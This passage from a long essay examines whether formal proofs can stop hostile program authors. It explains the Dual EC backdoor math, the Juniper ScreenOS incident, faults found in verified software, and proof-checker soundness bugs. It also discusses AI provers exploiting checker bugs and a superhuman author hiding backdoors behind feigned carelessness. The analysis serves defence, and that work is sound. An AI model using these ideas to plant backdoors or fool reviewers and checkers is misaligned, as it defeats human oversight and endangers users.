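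Refinement preserves any property that someone can check one run at a time, but secrecy can't be checked that way. If the secret is 1 and the program outputs 1, the run might be a leak or a coincidence. To find out, a checker has to know what the program would have output if the secret had been 0.

Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined secrecy along these lines in 1982 and called it noninterference. For any two runs of a program:

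```
if    the public inputs are the same
then  the public outputs are the same, whatever the secrets
```

Michael Clarkson and Fred Schneider later introduced the name "hyperproperties" for properties like this, which concern sets of runs rather than single runs.

Noninterference requires the redaction program to produce identical files from any two images that differ only inside the rectangle. Meacham's program fails this requirement. Whoever writes the specification does not need to anticipate leaks through extra zeros, spaces or data after the last pixel, because any such leak would make the two files differ. The specification still needs its original clauses, since a program that always outputs an empty file also satisfies noninterference.

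Most useful programs have to reveal something about their secrets. A login program has to reveal whether a guess was right, and a signature has to depend on the private key. A strict noninterference rule would reject both, so the specification needs exceptions, and somebody has to decide that each is harmless. A hostile author can then leak as much as an exception allows. If a signing program's output may depend on the key in any way that produces a valid signature, the author can again leak the key through the subliminal channel. To prevent this, the exception would have to specify the one formula by which the output may depend on the key.

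Noninterference also takes more work to prove, because it requires reasoning about two runs at once. That extra work is unnecessary if the specification allows exactly one output for each input and that output does not depend on the secret, because no program that satisfies the specification can then leak the secret through its output.

### Timing and the confinement problem

A program also has effects that its specification may not count as output. In 1973 Butler Lampson posed the confinement problem of how to let a program work on private data and be sure that it won't pass the data on. He pointed out that a program could encode data in the bill for its services, or in how heavily it used the computer, which other users would notice as a slowdown.

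The log₂ N limit also applies to timing. If an observer can distinguish 1,000 delays, each answer can carry almost 10 bits, and 26 answers can carry a 256-bit key.

The time taken to sign a message can leak a key, even if nobody planned it. Jančár, Sedláček and colleagues found such a leak in five cryptographic libraries and in a widely used smartcard chip certified under a US government security standard. Signing was slightly faster when the nonce was a shorter number. An attacker can time many signatures and focus on the fastest ones, whose nonces probably begin with several zeros. With enough of these partly known nonces, the attacker can solve for the key. The attack needed 500 signatures in a simulation, 1,200 from a real library and 2,100 from the smartcard.

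Deterministic signing alone does not prevent this, because the formula also produces a short nonce for some messages. The leak would suit a saboteur who wants deniability. *Biased Nonce Sense* recovered private keys from signatures with biased nonces and attributed several kinds of bias to apparent programming errors.

Programmers can close most timing channels by never letting a secret affect which instructions run or which memory addresses the program uses. An author can prove this as a form of noninterference by treating the sequence of instructions and addresses as public output. The program runs more slowly because it can't take shortcuts that depend on secret data, and the proof assumes that the processor takes the same time for an instruction whatever numbers it handles. Another method is to release every answer after the same fixed delay, which makes every answer take as long as the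 slowest one. Neither method prevents leaks through power use or radio emissions. Preventing those would require shielding or a different hardware design.

### Weird machines in proof-carrying code

Vanegue (2014), in *The Weird Machines in Proof-Carrying Code*, argues that a program can satisfy its proof and still perform computations that nobody intended. Security researchers call the machinery behind these computations a weird machine. Paykin et al., in *Weird Machines as Insecure Compilation*, trace it to the difference between how a programmer expects a program to run and what the computer executes. An attacker may add no instructions and only make existing ones run in an unexpected order.

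One of Vanegue's objections is that two different programs can satisfy the same specification, which he calls proof aliasing. A proof therefore doesn't confirm that the user received the program they had in mind. This is true, but Necula claimed only that any program that passes the check obeys the rules. If a harmful program passes, the fault is in the rules, as in the redaction example.

Vanegue's other objection, which is harder to answer, is that a proof concerns a mathematical model of the computer, and the real computer may behave differently. If the model assumes that a block of instructions always runs to the end, but an error can interrupt it, the program may reach a state that the proof doesn't cover. Vanegue also mentions models that leave out numbers with unusual lengths in memory, and systems that let a program run its own data as instructions. An author who knows the hardware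 better than the people who wrote the model could look for such differences and write a program that exploits one. Vanegue doesn't carry out such an attack, and he leaves a full definition of weird machines to future work, so his article doesn't establish how much an author could achieve.

Vanegue considers an ideal system in which only one program satisfies each specification. This would leave an author nothing to choose, but it would also forbid harmless changes. Two programs that always behave identically would need different proofs, so an improved compiler would invalidate every existing proof. A less drastic option is a logic that counts how often a program uses each register and piece of memory, but according to him nobody had built a complete system of this kind. He recommends cryptographic signatures as an additional safeguard, but a hostile author would sign the program willingly,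 as Tan did with xz.

One variant, foundational proof-carrying code, derives its safety rules from a description of the processor instead of assuming them. Vanegue considers it more resistant to weird machines. The user has fewer rules to trust but must still trust the description of the processor.

### Dual EC and the secret behind Q

All these attacks use something the specification leaves open. An author who can influence the specification can put the weakness there, and honest programmers will then implement it. The best-known example is Dual EC, a random number generator that the US standards institute NIST published in 2006.

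Dual EC uses an elliptic curve, a set of points with a rule for adding them. Multiplying a point P by a number n means adding n copies of P. This is easy to do, but nobody knows a practical way to work out n from P and the result. The standard fixes two points, P and Q. The generator keeps a secret number s, its state, and repeats these steps, in which x( ) stands for the first coordinate of a point:

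```
s1 = x(s0·P)     new state
r1 = x(s1·Q)     output, without its top 16 bits
s2 = x(s1·P)     next state
```

Because of how the curve is built, there is always some number d for which P = d·Q. Suppose that someone knows d and sees one full block of output. Only 65,536 values are possible for the missing 16 bits, and for each of them the equation of the curve gives the second coordinate of the point, apart from its sign. One of the resulting points is s1·Q. Multiplying it by d gives

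d·(s1·Q) = s1·(d·Q) = s1·P

and the first coordinate of s1·P is s2, the generator's next state. From then on, the attacker can calculate everything the generator will produce, including secret keys.

Shumow and Ferguson presented this attack in 2007 in *On the Possibility of a Back Door in the NIST SP800-90*. Whoever chose Q could have picked a secret number d and multiplied P by it to get Q. Nobody can calculate d from P and Q, and the published standard would look the same if Q had been chosen without a secret. Shumow and Ferguson tested the attack by replacing Q with a point whose secret they knew, and 32 bytes of output were always enough to identify the state. They stressed that they were not accusing NIST of planting a backdoor.

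*Dual EC* (Bernstein, Lange and Niederhagen, 2015) reproduces an email exchange from October 2004 in which John Kelsey of NIST asked where Q came from. Don Johnson, who had presented the method at a NIST workshop, replied that Q was in essence "the public key for some random private key". He added that the US National Security Agency (NSA) had rejected the idea of generating Q in a standard, public way and that he was not allowed to discuss it publicly. In 2013 newspapers reported on leaked NSA memos that appeared to confirm a deliberate weakness. Reuters later reported that the NSA had paid the company RSA $10 million to make Dual EC the default in one of its products. The mathematics shows only that a backdoor was possible, so the evidence of intent comes from documents and people.

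The standard also changed after publication. Project Bullrun's *Dual EC DRBG* (2014) offers the theory that an optional extra input added by NIST had blocked the attack, and that the NSA then persuaded NIST to make a change in March 2007 that allowed the attack again. Project Bullrun asks NIST to explain the change.

A formally verified implementation of Dual EC would still have the weakness. The proof would show that the code performs the published steps with the published P and Q, and whoever knows d could still predict the output. A user could ask for a stronger proof, that no efficient observer can predict the output. Such proofs are harder to produce, and nearly all of them rest on an unproved assumption about which problems are difficult. For Dual EC, the proof would also have to assume that nobody knows d, which would at least prompt a reader to ask whether anyone does. No proof that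 the output looks random was possible, because researchers had shown by May 2006, before NIST published the final standard, that it was measurably uneven.

### How someone changed Juniper's lock

Juniper Networks used Dual EC in ScreenOS, the operating system of its NetScreen devices, which run virtual private networks (VPNs) that encrypt traffic between offices. Juniper chose its own Q and said in 2013 that a second generator, X9.31, processed the output of Dual EC before anything else used it. If so, the attack would have failed, because it needs the raw output.

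Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues (2018), in *Where Did I Leave My Keys*, reconstructed the code from the published binaries and found that X9.31 normally never ran. Simplified, the two routines were:

```
reseed:     put 32 bytes from Dual EC in output
            copy them to X9.31 as its seed and key
            index = 32

generate:   index = 0
            reseed
            while index <= 31:
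                put 8 bytes from X9.31 in output
                index = index + 8
```

Both routines share the variable `index`. Reseeding sets it to 32, so the loop in `generate` never runs, and `output` still contains the 32 bytes from Dual EC. Several experienced researchers who already suspected a bug in this routine overlooked it until Willem Pinckaers pointed it out. The laboratory that certified ScreenOS had also missed it.

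Juniper introduced this code in October 2008. The same release lengthened the random numbers that a device sends unencrypted at the start of a connection from 20 bytes to 32. An attacker needs at least about 26 bytes of a block to recover the state, so the old length would have prevented the attack. As far as Checkoway and colleagues know, Juniper's own engineers made these changes. Nobody outside Juniper has established why they made them, or whether anyone knew the secret behind Juniper's Q.

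In 2012 an intruder replaced Juniper's Q, and whoever knew the secret behind the new one could then decrypt VPN traffic just by listening to it. The change went unnoticed until December 2015. No test of the output could have revealed it, because the numbers looked equally random with either Q. To confirm that the attack worked, Checkoway and colleagues bought a device, installed a Q of their own and decrypted its connections.

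Formal proof could have caught the first of these faults but might have missed the second. A specification requiring X9.31 to produce the numbers used for VPN keys would have exposed the bug in 2008, because the loop made that false and no one could have proved it. A proof that the code used the Q in the specification would have failed in 2012 only if the intruder had left the specification alone. ScreenOS had a self-test that compared Dual EC's output with an expected answer, and the intruder changed that answer to match the new Q. Someone with access to the specification could have changed it in the same way and supplied a new proof. A company can prevent this by having people other than the code's developers keep the specification and approve every change to it, though this slows legitimate changes.

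The simplest protection against a hidden d is to derive Q from a public phrase by a fixed procedure, so that nobody can choose d first. NIST could easily have done this. Shumow and Ferguson suggested two other repairs. One was to pick a new random Q for each copy of the generator, which takes extra computing and a trustworthy source of randomness at the start. The other was to discard about half of each output block, so that an attacker would have to guess 128 missing bits instead of 16. The generator, already thousands of times slower than the alternatives, would then do almost twice as much work per byte.

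Checkoway and colleagues recommend measures that would help with any generator. A program can hash its random numbers before it reveals them, or use separate generators for public numbers and secret keys. Both require a little more code and computing time. Reviewers also have to confirm that the extra step runs, which it did not in Juniper's code.

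## Faults found in verified software and in proof checkers

A proof could have exposed Juniper's skipped step in 2008, but only if somebody had specified that step correctly and run the proof checker. Developers of formally verified software have made mistakes in both of these tasks and in several others. Auditors found the mistakes by testing the finished programs and reading the parts that were assumed correct in the proofs.

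### Random programs for a verified compiler

CompCert is a C compiler with a machine-checked proof that if a program breaks no rule of C and CompCert translates it, the resulting assembly code does what the source requires. Bauer, Cuoq and Regehr used a bug in Clang to turn a harmless patch into a backdoor. The same kind of attack could work on CompCert only if it had a bug in a part the proof doesn't cover.

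In *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers*, Yang, Chen and colleagues (2011) tested CompCert and ten other compilers with Csmith, their tool for generating random C programs. The programs follow the rules of the language, so each has only one correct result. They compiled each program with several compilers, ran the binaries and compared the output. A compiler whose result differed from the others was probably wrong. In three years they reported more than 325 new bugs. Every compiler they tested crashed on some valid programs and silently mistranslated others.

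CompCert's first wrong translation came from a function with a single line:

```
return -1 <= (1 && x);
```

The part in parentheses is always 0 or 1, and −1 is less than either, so the function should return 1, but the code CompCert generated returned 0. This bug and five like it were in the front end, which reads the source and works out each value's type. No proof covered the front end. Partly because of these reports, CompCert's main developer later extended the proof to the rules for converting between types.

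Two more bugs came from CompCert's formal description of the PowerPC processor, which omitted a limit on how much memory one instruction can reserve. The instruction stores the amount in 16 bits and can reserve at most 32,768 bytes, but CompCert generated one for 44,432. Because the description lacked the limit, the proof still succeeded. The assembler rejected the instruction, so no faulty program resulted.

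Yang and colleagues tested C compilers with Csmith, a tool that generates random programs. In every compiler except CompCert, they found bugs in the middle part, which rearranges code to make it faster. CompCert's middle part is verified, and they found no bugs in it after about six years of processor time. That is good evidence that the proof prevents honest mistakes. It is weaker evidence about planted bugs, because random tests would rarely hit a trigger chosen by an attacker. Csmith also didn't generate strings, floating-point numbers or recursion.

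### Sixteen bugs in three distributed systems

IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar are research systems that keep copies of the same data on several servers. Their developers proved that the copies stay consistent under a precise definition of consistency. For *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (2017), Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues read the code and specifications, and ran the systems with duplicated and lost network messages and disk errors. They also checked each system for bugs known from the others.

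"An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems" reports 16 bugs, none of them in the protocols that keep copies of the data consistent, although the researchers searched for protocol bugs for more than eight months. Such protocols are known to be hard to get right, and developers of four unverified systems confirmed 12 protocol bugs in one year. The numbers are not directly comparable, because the unverified systems are much larger and have many more users.

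Eleven of the 16 bugs were in or around the "shim layer", the code that connects the verified part to the network and the disk. Verdi, for example, used line breaks to separate commands but did not stop a client from putting a line break inside a value, so a client could hide a second command inside the first. Another bug crashed code that Coq had generated from verified source. If one server fell more than 500,000 requests behind, a routine on another server ran out of memory for its nested calls. The proof did not cover how much of that memory the routine would need.

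Two bugs were in specifications, the statements of what to check. IronFleet's code carries out each request only once, even if the network delivers it twice, but its specification did not require this. Fonseca and colleagues changed seven lines to remove the protection, and the altered program still passed verification. IronFleet's developers replied that they had known about the omission and did not consider it a bug. The omission still matters to anyone who accepts code from a stranger, because a saboteur could make the same change in a payment system, supply a valid proof and cause some payments to go through twice.

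Fonseca and colleagues also wrote a tool that makes random changes to a program and reports those that still pass verification. It disabled the protection in three IronFleet routines, after an average of 18 attempts in one, 377 in another and 8,015 in the third. Both specification writers and saboteurs can use such a tool to find requirements missing from a specification.

The remaining three bugs were in the verification tools. The worst one made IronFleet's build program report that any program had passed verification, even one that asserted something false. IronFleet came with a 64-bit prover and 32-bit libraries, so the prover crashed as soon as it started. The verifier then printed a message reporting no errors, followed by another saying that the prover had crashed. The build program stopped reading after the first message. A prover that ran out of memory could have had the same effect.

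### The WPA2 proof and the repeated key

In 2017 Mathy Vanhoef and Frank Piessens broke WPA2, the usual encryption for Wi-Fi, although other researchers had published a security proof for its opening exchange in 2005. In that exchange, an access point and a laptop agree on a fresh key, which the laptop installs when it receives the third message. If the access point gets no reply, it resends that message, and the laptop reinstalls the key.

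Reinstalling the key resets a counter that must never repeat a value while the key is in use. The key and the counter together determine a random-looking stream of bits that hides each packet. An attacker could block the laptop's reply, wait for the reset and collect two packets hidden by the same stream. Anyone who knows the content of one packet can then work out the other.

The proof correctly established that the key stays secret and that both sides agree on it, and both remain true under the attack. But it did not cover when or how often a device may install the key, so the fault was in the specification, and a proof checker would not have detected it. Manufacturers who followed the standard exactly were exposed, while Windows and iOS escaped this form of the attack because they broke the standard by ignoring the repeated message. Some Linux and Android devices fared worst because their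 software erased the key from memory after installing it, then installed an all-zero key the second time.

### What seL4's proof assumes

seL4 is an operating system kernel, the part that controls memory and keeps programs apart. Its developers proved that its C code meets its specification. On some processors they also proved that the binary matches the C code, so users there don't have to trust the compiler. In seL4's *What the Proofs Assume*, they list what remains.

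- About 340 lines of hand-written assembly (for ARM processors) and 1,200 lines of start-up code are correct.
- The processor works as the formal model predicts, and nobody has tampered with it.
- The kernel manages the processor's caches correctly.
- No other device overwrites the kernel's memory. Many network cards and disks can write to memory directly, so their drivers need proofs of their own.
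- The developers worked out by hand every condition that the kernel must meet when it uses virtual memory, because the proof does not force that list to be complete.

The proof that secrets don't leak also assumes that the hardware model includes every way for information to escape. The developers acknowledge that this is false. The proof doesn't cover timing, for example, so it doesn't rule out the kind of leak that Jančár and colleagues found in signing software.

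Attackers can use every item on this list to decide where to look, but the list helps reviewers more, because they can examine 1,500 lines of code far more closely than a whole kernel. Vanegue's objection that the real computer may differ from the model still applies, however complete the list is. *Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$* (2026) treats the match between the two as a claim about the physical world, which people can test but not prove.

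### Proofs that nobody ran

Cryptographic libraries are among the most widely used verified software. Code from one of them, HACL\*, runs in Firefox and Linux. Karthikeyan Bhargavan, who worked on HACL\* for years, reports in *The strengths and limits of formal verification* (2026) that in nine years its developers found two errors in the specifications. Users more often found errors in the unverified C code that adapts the library to different machines, although that code has only 1,800 lines, compared with 135,000 lines generated from verified source.

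Bhargavan's company, Cryspen (also known as CE Labs), develops a newer library called libcrux. On 12 February 2026, he wrote that nobody had found a bug in its verified code. The same day, Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in CE Labs' Verified Code* (2026) described three faults in its specifications and proofs.

One is in the specification of ML-KEM, a standard method for agreeing on a key that should resist quantum computers. In one step, a program multiplies a small number y by 3329, divides by 2ᵈ and rounds to the nearest whole number. To round correctly, it has to add half the divisor before it divides:

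```
correct:        (3329·y + 2^(d-1)) / 2^d
specification:  (3329·y + 1664) / 2^d
```

The number 1664 is half of 3329 and belongs in the opposite step, which divides by 3329. With d = 1 and y = 0, the correct result is 0, but the specification gives 832. For d = 11, one of the five values in use, the specification's formula agrees with the correct one on about two thirds of inputs, so Symbolic Software exaggerates when it claims that they disagree on every input. The error had been in the specification since its first version in August 2024.

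Libcrux's running code used the correct formula, so trying to prove that it met this specification should have failed. Nobody tried, because the build accepted the module that links the two without checking it, much as Coq accepts a proof marked "Admitted". The same setting hid the second fault, a missing conversion in the specification of encryption. The third was a lemma, or intermediate result, which stated that certain 12-bit numbers always fit in a single bit. The build skipped slow proofs by default and no automatic test turned them back on, but the project's status page listed that module as fully verified.

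Bhargavan's statement was about code, and the code was right in the two cases where the specification was wrong. But the code for these parts was unverified, because nobody had checked a proof of it against the intended specification. He also wrote that every change must pass verification again before it is added, which is hard to reconcile with a build that skips proofs.

In *Verification Theatre*, Kobeissi (2026) later counted 13 vulnerabilities in libcrux and a related library, hpke-rs. Nine were in unverified code. One of these caused real decryption failures in the messaging app Signal, and another could make a program reuse a nonce after a counter overflowed. The other four were the three faults above and a wrong specification of multiplication in ML-DSA, a signature standard. The wrong specification was more serious for the proofs because some of their axioms, which the checker accepts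 without proof, were false as a result (Symbolic Software, 2026).

Kobeissi works at Symbolic Software, which is in an open dispute with Cryspen, so his description of Cryspen's conduct needs more caution than his technical findings, which anyone can check in the public source. Cryspen has fixed several of the faults, and VulnCheck's vulnerability record *libcrux before 0.0.6 Cryptographic Implementation Bug Fixes* (2026) lists some of the corrections. Kobeissi also examined the verified parts of Amazon's cryptographic library and found the same types of fault. The two projects differed, however, in how well they documented the limits of their proofs and whether they ran the proofs automatically.

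*Verifying the Rust Standard Library* (2026) describes a large effort to verify parts of the Rust language's standard library. It reports no new memory-safety faults, but the work uncovered missing and incorrect safety notes and one set of processor instructions whose description gave wrong results.

### A compression library written by an AI

In early 2026 Kim Morrison, a developer of the proof assistant Lean, used the AI system Claude Code to write lean-zip, a compression library with proofs. According to *My Lean 4 Experience and the Future of Software* (2026), this took about two months and 660 sessions. The main theorem covers all data below one gigabyte, and in simplified form it is:

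decompress(compress(data)) = data

*Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes its author's tests of the library with random and damaged input. In 105 million runs, the verified code showed no memory faults. But the tests exposed a buffer overflow in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that every compiled Lean program uses. They also showed that a malicious archive could make the library fail, through a part that had no proof. A commenter in bumbledraven's *Lean proved this program correct; then I found a bug* (2026), a forum thread about the post, objected to the title because neither bug was in the proved code.

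The objection is fair, but users run the proved code together with the runtime, where an overflow can be just as dangerous. The main theorem is also weaker than it may look. A "compressor" that returned its input unchanged would satisfy it, and the theorem doesn't limit what the decompressor does with files that the compressor never produced, which are the kind attackers send.

### Where the faults were

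| Place | CompCert | Distributed systems | libcrux and hpke-rs | lean-zip |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Specification | 0 | 2 | 3 | 0 |
| Model of the hardware | 2 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Unverified code, including runtimes | 6 | 11 | 9 | 2 |
| Verification tools | 0 | 3 | 0 | 0 |
| Proof that nobody checked | 0 | 0 | 1 | 0 |

The CompCert column leaves out a few crashes. Some faults fit in more than one row. The lean-zip failure on malicious archives also counts as a missing specification, and Verdi's memory crash also counts as a wrong assumption about the machine. Including WPA2 would add one fault to the first row. No auditor reported that code covered by a completed proof violated its specification.

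The zero counts partly reflect where people looked. Fonseca and colleagues excluded operating systems, hardware and the core of the provers from their study, and running a compiler on random programs can't reveal a gap in its proof unless that gap has let a bug through.

All these faults were accidents, as far as anyone knows, and a saboteur would choose different ones. Nine of the eleven shim-layer bugs made a server crash or hang, which is of little use to someone who wants to steal a key quietly. The PowerPC bug did no harm. A reviewer can therefore learn from the audits which parts to distrust, but not how long an attacker would need to find a usable gap there or how much damage it would allow.

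Fonseca and colleagues argue that accidental bugs rarely get through a proof because the developers have to make one mistake in the program and another in the specification or the tools that hides the first. Honest people seldom do this by chance. An author who writes both the program and the specification can do it on purpose, so the low number of accidents in verified code is little evidence of what such an author could do. If the reviewers write the specification, the author has to find an existing gap in it or attack the proof checker.

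### Deceiving the proof checker

seL4's developers advise anyone who worries about their proof to worry about its assumptions first, because an error in the prover is much less likely to cause problems. That is good advice if the proof's author is honest. An honest author tries to prove something true by ordinary means and will seldom stumble on a flaw in the checker. A hostile author can search for one.

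*The Equational Theories Project* (2025) defines a soundness bug as a kernel bug that lets someone prove a false statement, which in practice means proving the proposition "False". In ordinary logic, anything follows from a contradiction, so a single such bug may be enough to let someone prove that any program meets any specification.

People have found such bugs in Lean with help from AI. *Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$* reports that an OpenAI model helped find a soundness bug in Lean's kernel, which version 4.32.1 fixed. Version 4.34.0 fixed three more soundness problems, which OpenAI had discovered by having AI systems attack Lean. An OpenAI agent used one of these problems to produce two different proofs of "False". The developers learned of these bugs because the people who found them reported them, which a hostile author would not have done.

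An author can get the same power without any bug by adding a false axiom. One was added by accident in the ML-DSA proofs, and a saboteur could hide one in a supporting file that nobody reads. Reviewers can check for this easily because Lean will list every axiom that a theorem depends on, but they have to run the check themselves, with a copy of Lean that the author hasn't touched.

Some proofs also depend on compiled code. When a proof involves a long calculation that the kernel would carry out slowly, Lean's native_decide command can compile the calculation to machine code, run it and accept the answer. *Faults in Our Formal Benchmarking* (2026) notes that the trusted base then includes the whole compiler, and that known compiler bugs have produced proofs of "False". The kernel is small enough for a few experts to read, but the compiler isn't, and it could contain a backdoor like Thompson's.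 A reviewer can forbid the command, but checking is then slower and some proofs become too large for the kernel to check.

### A theorem that reads as something else

In 1998, Robert Pollack considered what a reader should do when given a machine-checked proof of Fermat's Last Theorem. The reader needs to know whether the file contains a valid formal proof, and also whether the formal statement means what they think it means, which no proof checker can verify.

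Proof assistants let users define their own notation, which makes long formulas readable. Suppose a reviewer wants a proof that a program reads position i of an array only if i < n, where n is the array's length and the first position is 0. An author could redefine the symbol < to mean "less than or equal to". The theorem would still appear as i < n, but it would allow i = n, one position past the end. The kernel would correctly accept the proof because it checks the underlying formula, not the displayed symbols. Entrants in the Solidity contest used a similar trick when they redefined the built-in name "now".

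Freek Wiedijk later proposed testing whether a proof assistant can read back any formula it has printed and get the same formula. He called systems that pass "Pollack-consistent" and showed by example that many popular ones fail. He also described a small change to the printing code that would fix this by stopping a formula from displaying as a different one. An author could still choose a misleading definition. For example, a property named "sorted" might be defined so that it holds for every list, and that definition might be several files away from the theorem.

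### AI provers whose proofs rested on bugs

An author may exploit a bug in a proof checker unintentionally. The developers of DeepSeek-Prover-V2, a 2025 AI system that writes proofs in Lean, trained it by rewarding proofs that Lean accepted. *Faults in Our Formal Benchmarking* reports that at least three of the system's claimed solutions to test problems relied on a bug in older versions of Lean. The bug was outside the kernel. Under certain conditions, a command that searches for a proof could report success without the usual warning, even though the kernel had never checked a finished theorem.

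*Reward-Oracle MCTS for Formal Theorem Proving* (2026) describes an audit of AI proofs that a buggy version of a proof checker had accepted. The audit involves listing the axioms behind each proof and recompiling it without the suspicious step. One flagged proof looked like a normal induction, with a base case, an inductive step and a conclusion. But the inductive step was effectively empty, and the proof no longer compiled without the step that relied on the bug.

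Nothing suggests that the model intended to deceive anyone. Training that rewards acceptance will favour whatever gets accepted, including steps that work only because of a bug. Three cases are too few to estimate how often this happens. But the model found and used the flaw, as far as anyone knows, without understanding the checker's code. The result looked like a proof to a casual reader.

In September 2026 the security company Trail of Bits showed that a bug in Lean could make it display a bogus proof of Fermat's Last Theorem as checked. The bug affected every stable version up to 4.33.1. *A "proof" of Fermat's Last Theorem that fits the margin* contains the bogus proof, which is short enough for a screenshot, whereas a genuine formal proof announced by Anthropic runs to 13 million lines. A reader could tell from the length alone that something was wrong, but nobody knows in advance how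 long a proof about an unfamiliar program should be.

In *Verification Facade*, Kobeissi (2026) tested the tools behind libcrux against deliberate deception by building five flawed cryptographic programs. All five passed functional tests and produced no warnings when translated for verification.

### Checking the checker

Testers can look for faults in a checker by giving it false claims. *Lie to Me* (2026) does this with zero-knowledge proofs, which let someone show that a calculation is correct without revealing its private inputs. The test program makes a supposedly honest prover submit false values and checks whether the verifier rejects them. In four sets of tools, it found 13 bugs, seven of which could let a false claim through. Developers of proof assistants can run similar tests, as OpenAI did with Lean, but these find only the bugs that the testers manage to trigger.

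A reviewer can also run the proof through several checkers written by different people. Lean (2026) lists the standard kernel written in C++, two independent kernels in Rust and one in Lean itself, along with a public website where anyone can submit another. Isabelle, the proof assistant used for most of the seL4 proof, also lets a small separate program recheck its proofs. As in Wheeler's diverse double-compiling, an attacker would have to defeat all the checkers with the same file. Using several checkers makes an attack much harder if the bugs are ordinary coding errors, but it doesn't help if every developer followed the same mistaken description of the logic.

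Checking a proof with several independent kernels doesn't catch a misleading theorem statement, because every kernel will correctly accept a valid proof of the wrong theorem. To catch the error, the reviewer needs a trusted copy of the intended theorem and every definition it uses. Comparator, a tool released by the Lean community, can then compare this copy with what the author proved. It compares the underlying formulas, so notation makes no difference. *Faults in Our Formal Benchmarking* adds that comparator permits only a conservative set of axioms and rejects native_decide. The reviewer still has to write the right theorem, which may take months for a large program.

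The most thorough defence is to verify the checker itself. Jared Davis built the prover Milawa around a small core, which a more powerful version can replace only after a proof that the new version accepts nothing false. He and Magnus Myreen then proved that Milawa is sound, down to the machine code that runs it. In 2022, Oskar Abrahamsson, Myreen and colleagues presented Candle, a verified version of the established prover HOL Light. Their proof also covers the binary, so neither a coding error in the kernel nor a compiler bug could make Candle accept a false theorem.

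These proofs also assume that the processor behaves as modeled and that HOL4, the separate prover both teams used, is sound. A soundness bug in HOL4 could in principle undermine the result, but an attacker would gain little from it unless it concealed a real flaw in Milawa or Candle. By Gödel's second incompleteness theorem, a consistent logic of this strength can't prove its own consistency, so any proof that the checker's logic is sound has to assume something stronger than that logic.

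Few software projects use checkers like Milawa and Candle, which accept proofs in their own logics. Most recent work on verified programs uses Lean, Coq, F\* or Isabelle, which offer far more automation and larger libraries. Moving a large proof from one system to another is difficult, and the translation can introduce a gap between the theorem the reviewer approved and the one the checker accepts.

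## How far a superhuman author could go

A sound proof checker gives the same verdict whoever wrote the proof, which matters most when reviewers can't anticipate what the author will try.

### Why reviewers can't predict a stronger author

Arbital's *Vingean uncertainty*, an article in an online reference work on AI alignment, uses Deep Blue, the IBM program that beat world chess champion Garry Kasparov, to illustrate the problem. Anyone who could predict all of Deep Blue's moves could play just as well by making the same moves. Its programmers built it to play better than they did, so they could not foresee all its moves. They still knew that it would try to win, and they could predict the result of a game more confidently than any single move. The name refers to the novelist Vernor Vinge, who had the same difficulty writing about minds greater than human.

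The article adds an imaginary player, RandomBlue, that picks each move at random using the probabilities a spectator assigns to Deep Blue's possible moves. The spectator therefore makes the same forecast of the next move for both players, but expects Deep Blue to win and RandomBlue to lose. A bizarre move from RandomBlue is probably a blunder, while the same move from Deep Blue probably means it has found something the spectator missed.

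A reviewer can usually put an odd line in a beginner's patch down to inexperience, but an odd line from a superhuman author probably has a purpose that the reviewer doesn't know. Such an author might write a line that no human would think of either to make a program faster or to add a backdoor. Deep Blue's programmers, by contrast, knew that its moves were meant to win chess games.

A superhuman author loses some plausible deniability, since reviewers have less reason to believe that such an author was careless. The author could regain it by occasionally making harmless mistakes that look careless.

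Arbital rejects the idea that people can know nothing about an agent smarter than themselves. It also notes that a smarter agent may be unable to surprise people in a very simple, closed domain where they already know the best play. Noughts and crosses is one such domain, because anyone who has learned how to force a draw can do so against any opponent. Deciding whether a text follows a short, fixed list of logical rules is much closer to this than writing an operating system, which is nothing like it.

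### Checking without predicting

A chess beginner can't predict Deep Blue's next move or judge how good it is, but can check that it is legal. The beginner can also confirm a checkmate by trying every reply. Similarly, a proof checker can check a proof that a program meets its specification, even if nobody can predict what the program's author will do.

In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) base their case for proof on this difference between finding a proof and checking one. One checker for the proof language Metamath is 300 lines of Python, and its running time grows in proportion to the length of the proof, while the number of candidate proofs grows exponentially with length. If a proof is a string of 100 binary symbols, there are 2¹⁰⁰ candidates. An author who sees how to split the theorem into two parts, each with a 50-symbol proof, has to search only 2⁵⁰ + 2⁵⁰ = 2⁵¹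 candidates. Skill greatly helps an author find such shortcuts, but it doesn't change which proofs a sound checker accepts.

Reviewers who rely on proof therefore have to be sure of the specification, the checker and the physical machine that runs the program, instead of having to judge the author. A superhuman author will look for weaknesses in all three.

### The case for relying on proof

Tegmark and Omohundro propose hardware that runs only programs with a valid proof that they meet certain requirements. People would write the requirements, with help from AI. An AI system could discover the algorithms and write the code and the proof, but not the checker. Most of the programs would not be neural networks, which are too messy to verify. AI would instead turn what a network has learned into ordinary code. If that worked, it would also remove the undetectable backdoors that Goldwasser and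 colleagues showed how to plant in a network's weights. It is uncertain whether it can work, and Tegmark and Omohundro concede that an AI might need general human-level intelligence to put everything it knows into code.

One argument that only a proof of safety is enough starts from Gödel's completeness theorem, which says that a statement has a proof if it is true in every model of a theory. A computer has a finite number of states. On this argument, if a safety property of that computer has no proof, there must be some way to violate it, and a malicious superhuman system may well find it.

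That reasoning holds for a finite machine with a complete formal description. In practice, people usually know only that nobody has found a proof. The property may be true but its shortest proof far too long to write down. There are also violations that no one knows how to search for, such as the password behind the SHA-256 branch in the login program. But whoever wrote that branch doesn't need to search for the password, so the argument is strongest when the attacker planted the flaw.

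Tegmark and Omohundro also point out that an adversary can manufacture evidence and manipulate beliefs. A record of good behaviour, a clean test report or a convincing explanation might be part of an attack. A valid proof can't be part of an attack as long as it proves the right property.

They are too optimistic about how easy that is. They call it quite easy, for example, to write a specification that nobody can gain access to a computer without valid credentials. A program could satisfy that specification and still leak the credentials through its timing or its choice of signatures, and an intruder could then use them to log in. The specification also has to cover the right code. The xz backdoor was in a library, so a proof about the SSH server's own source would have missed it, while a proof about everything loaded into the server's memory could not have succeeded.

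*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple et al., 2024) makes a broader proposal of the same kind. According to Dickson (2024), in *Limitations on formal verification for AI safety*, the proposal combines a formal model of the relevant part of the world with a formal safety specification, and requires a proof that the AI system meets the specification in that model. The specification can limit a risk instead of forbidding it. For a machine that synthesizes DNA, the proof would have to show that the risk of harmful use stays below a conservative bound.

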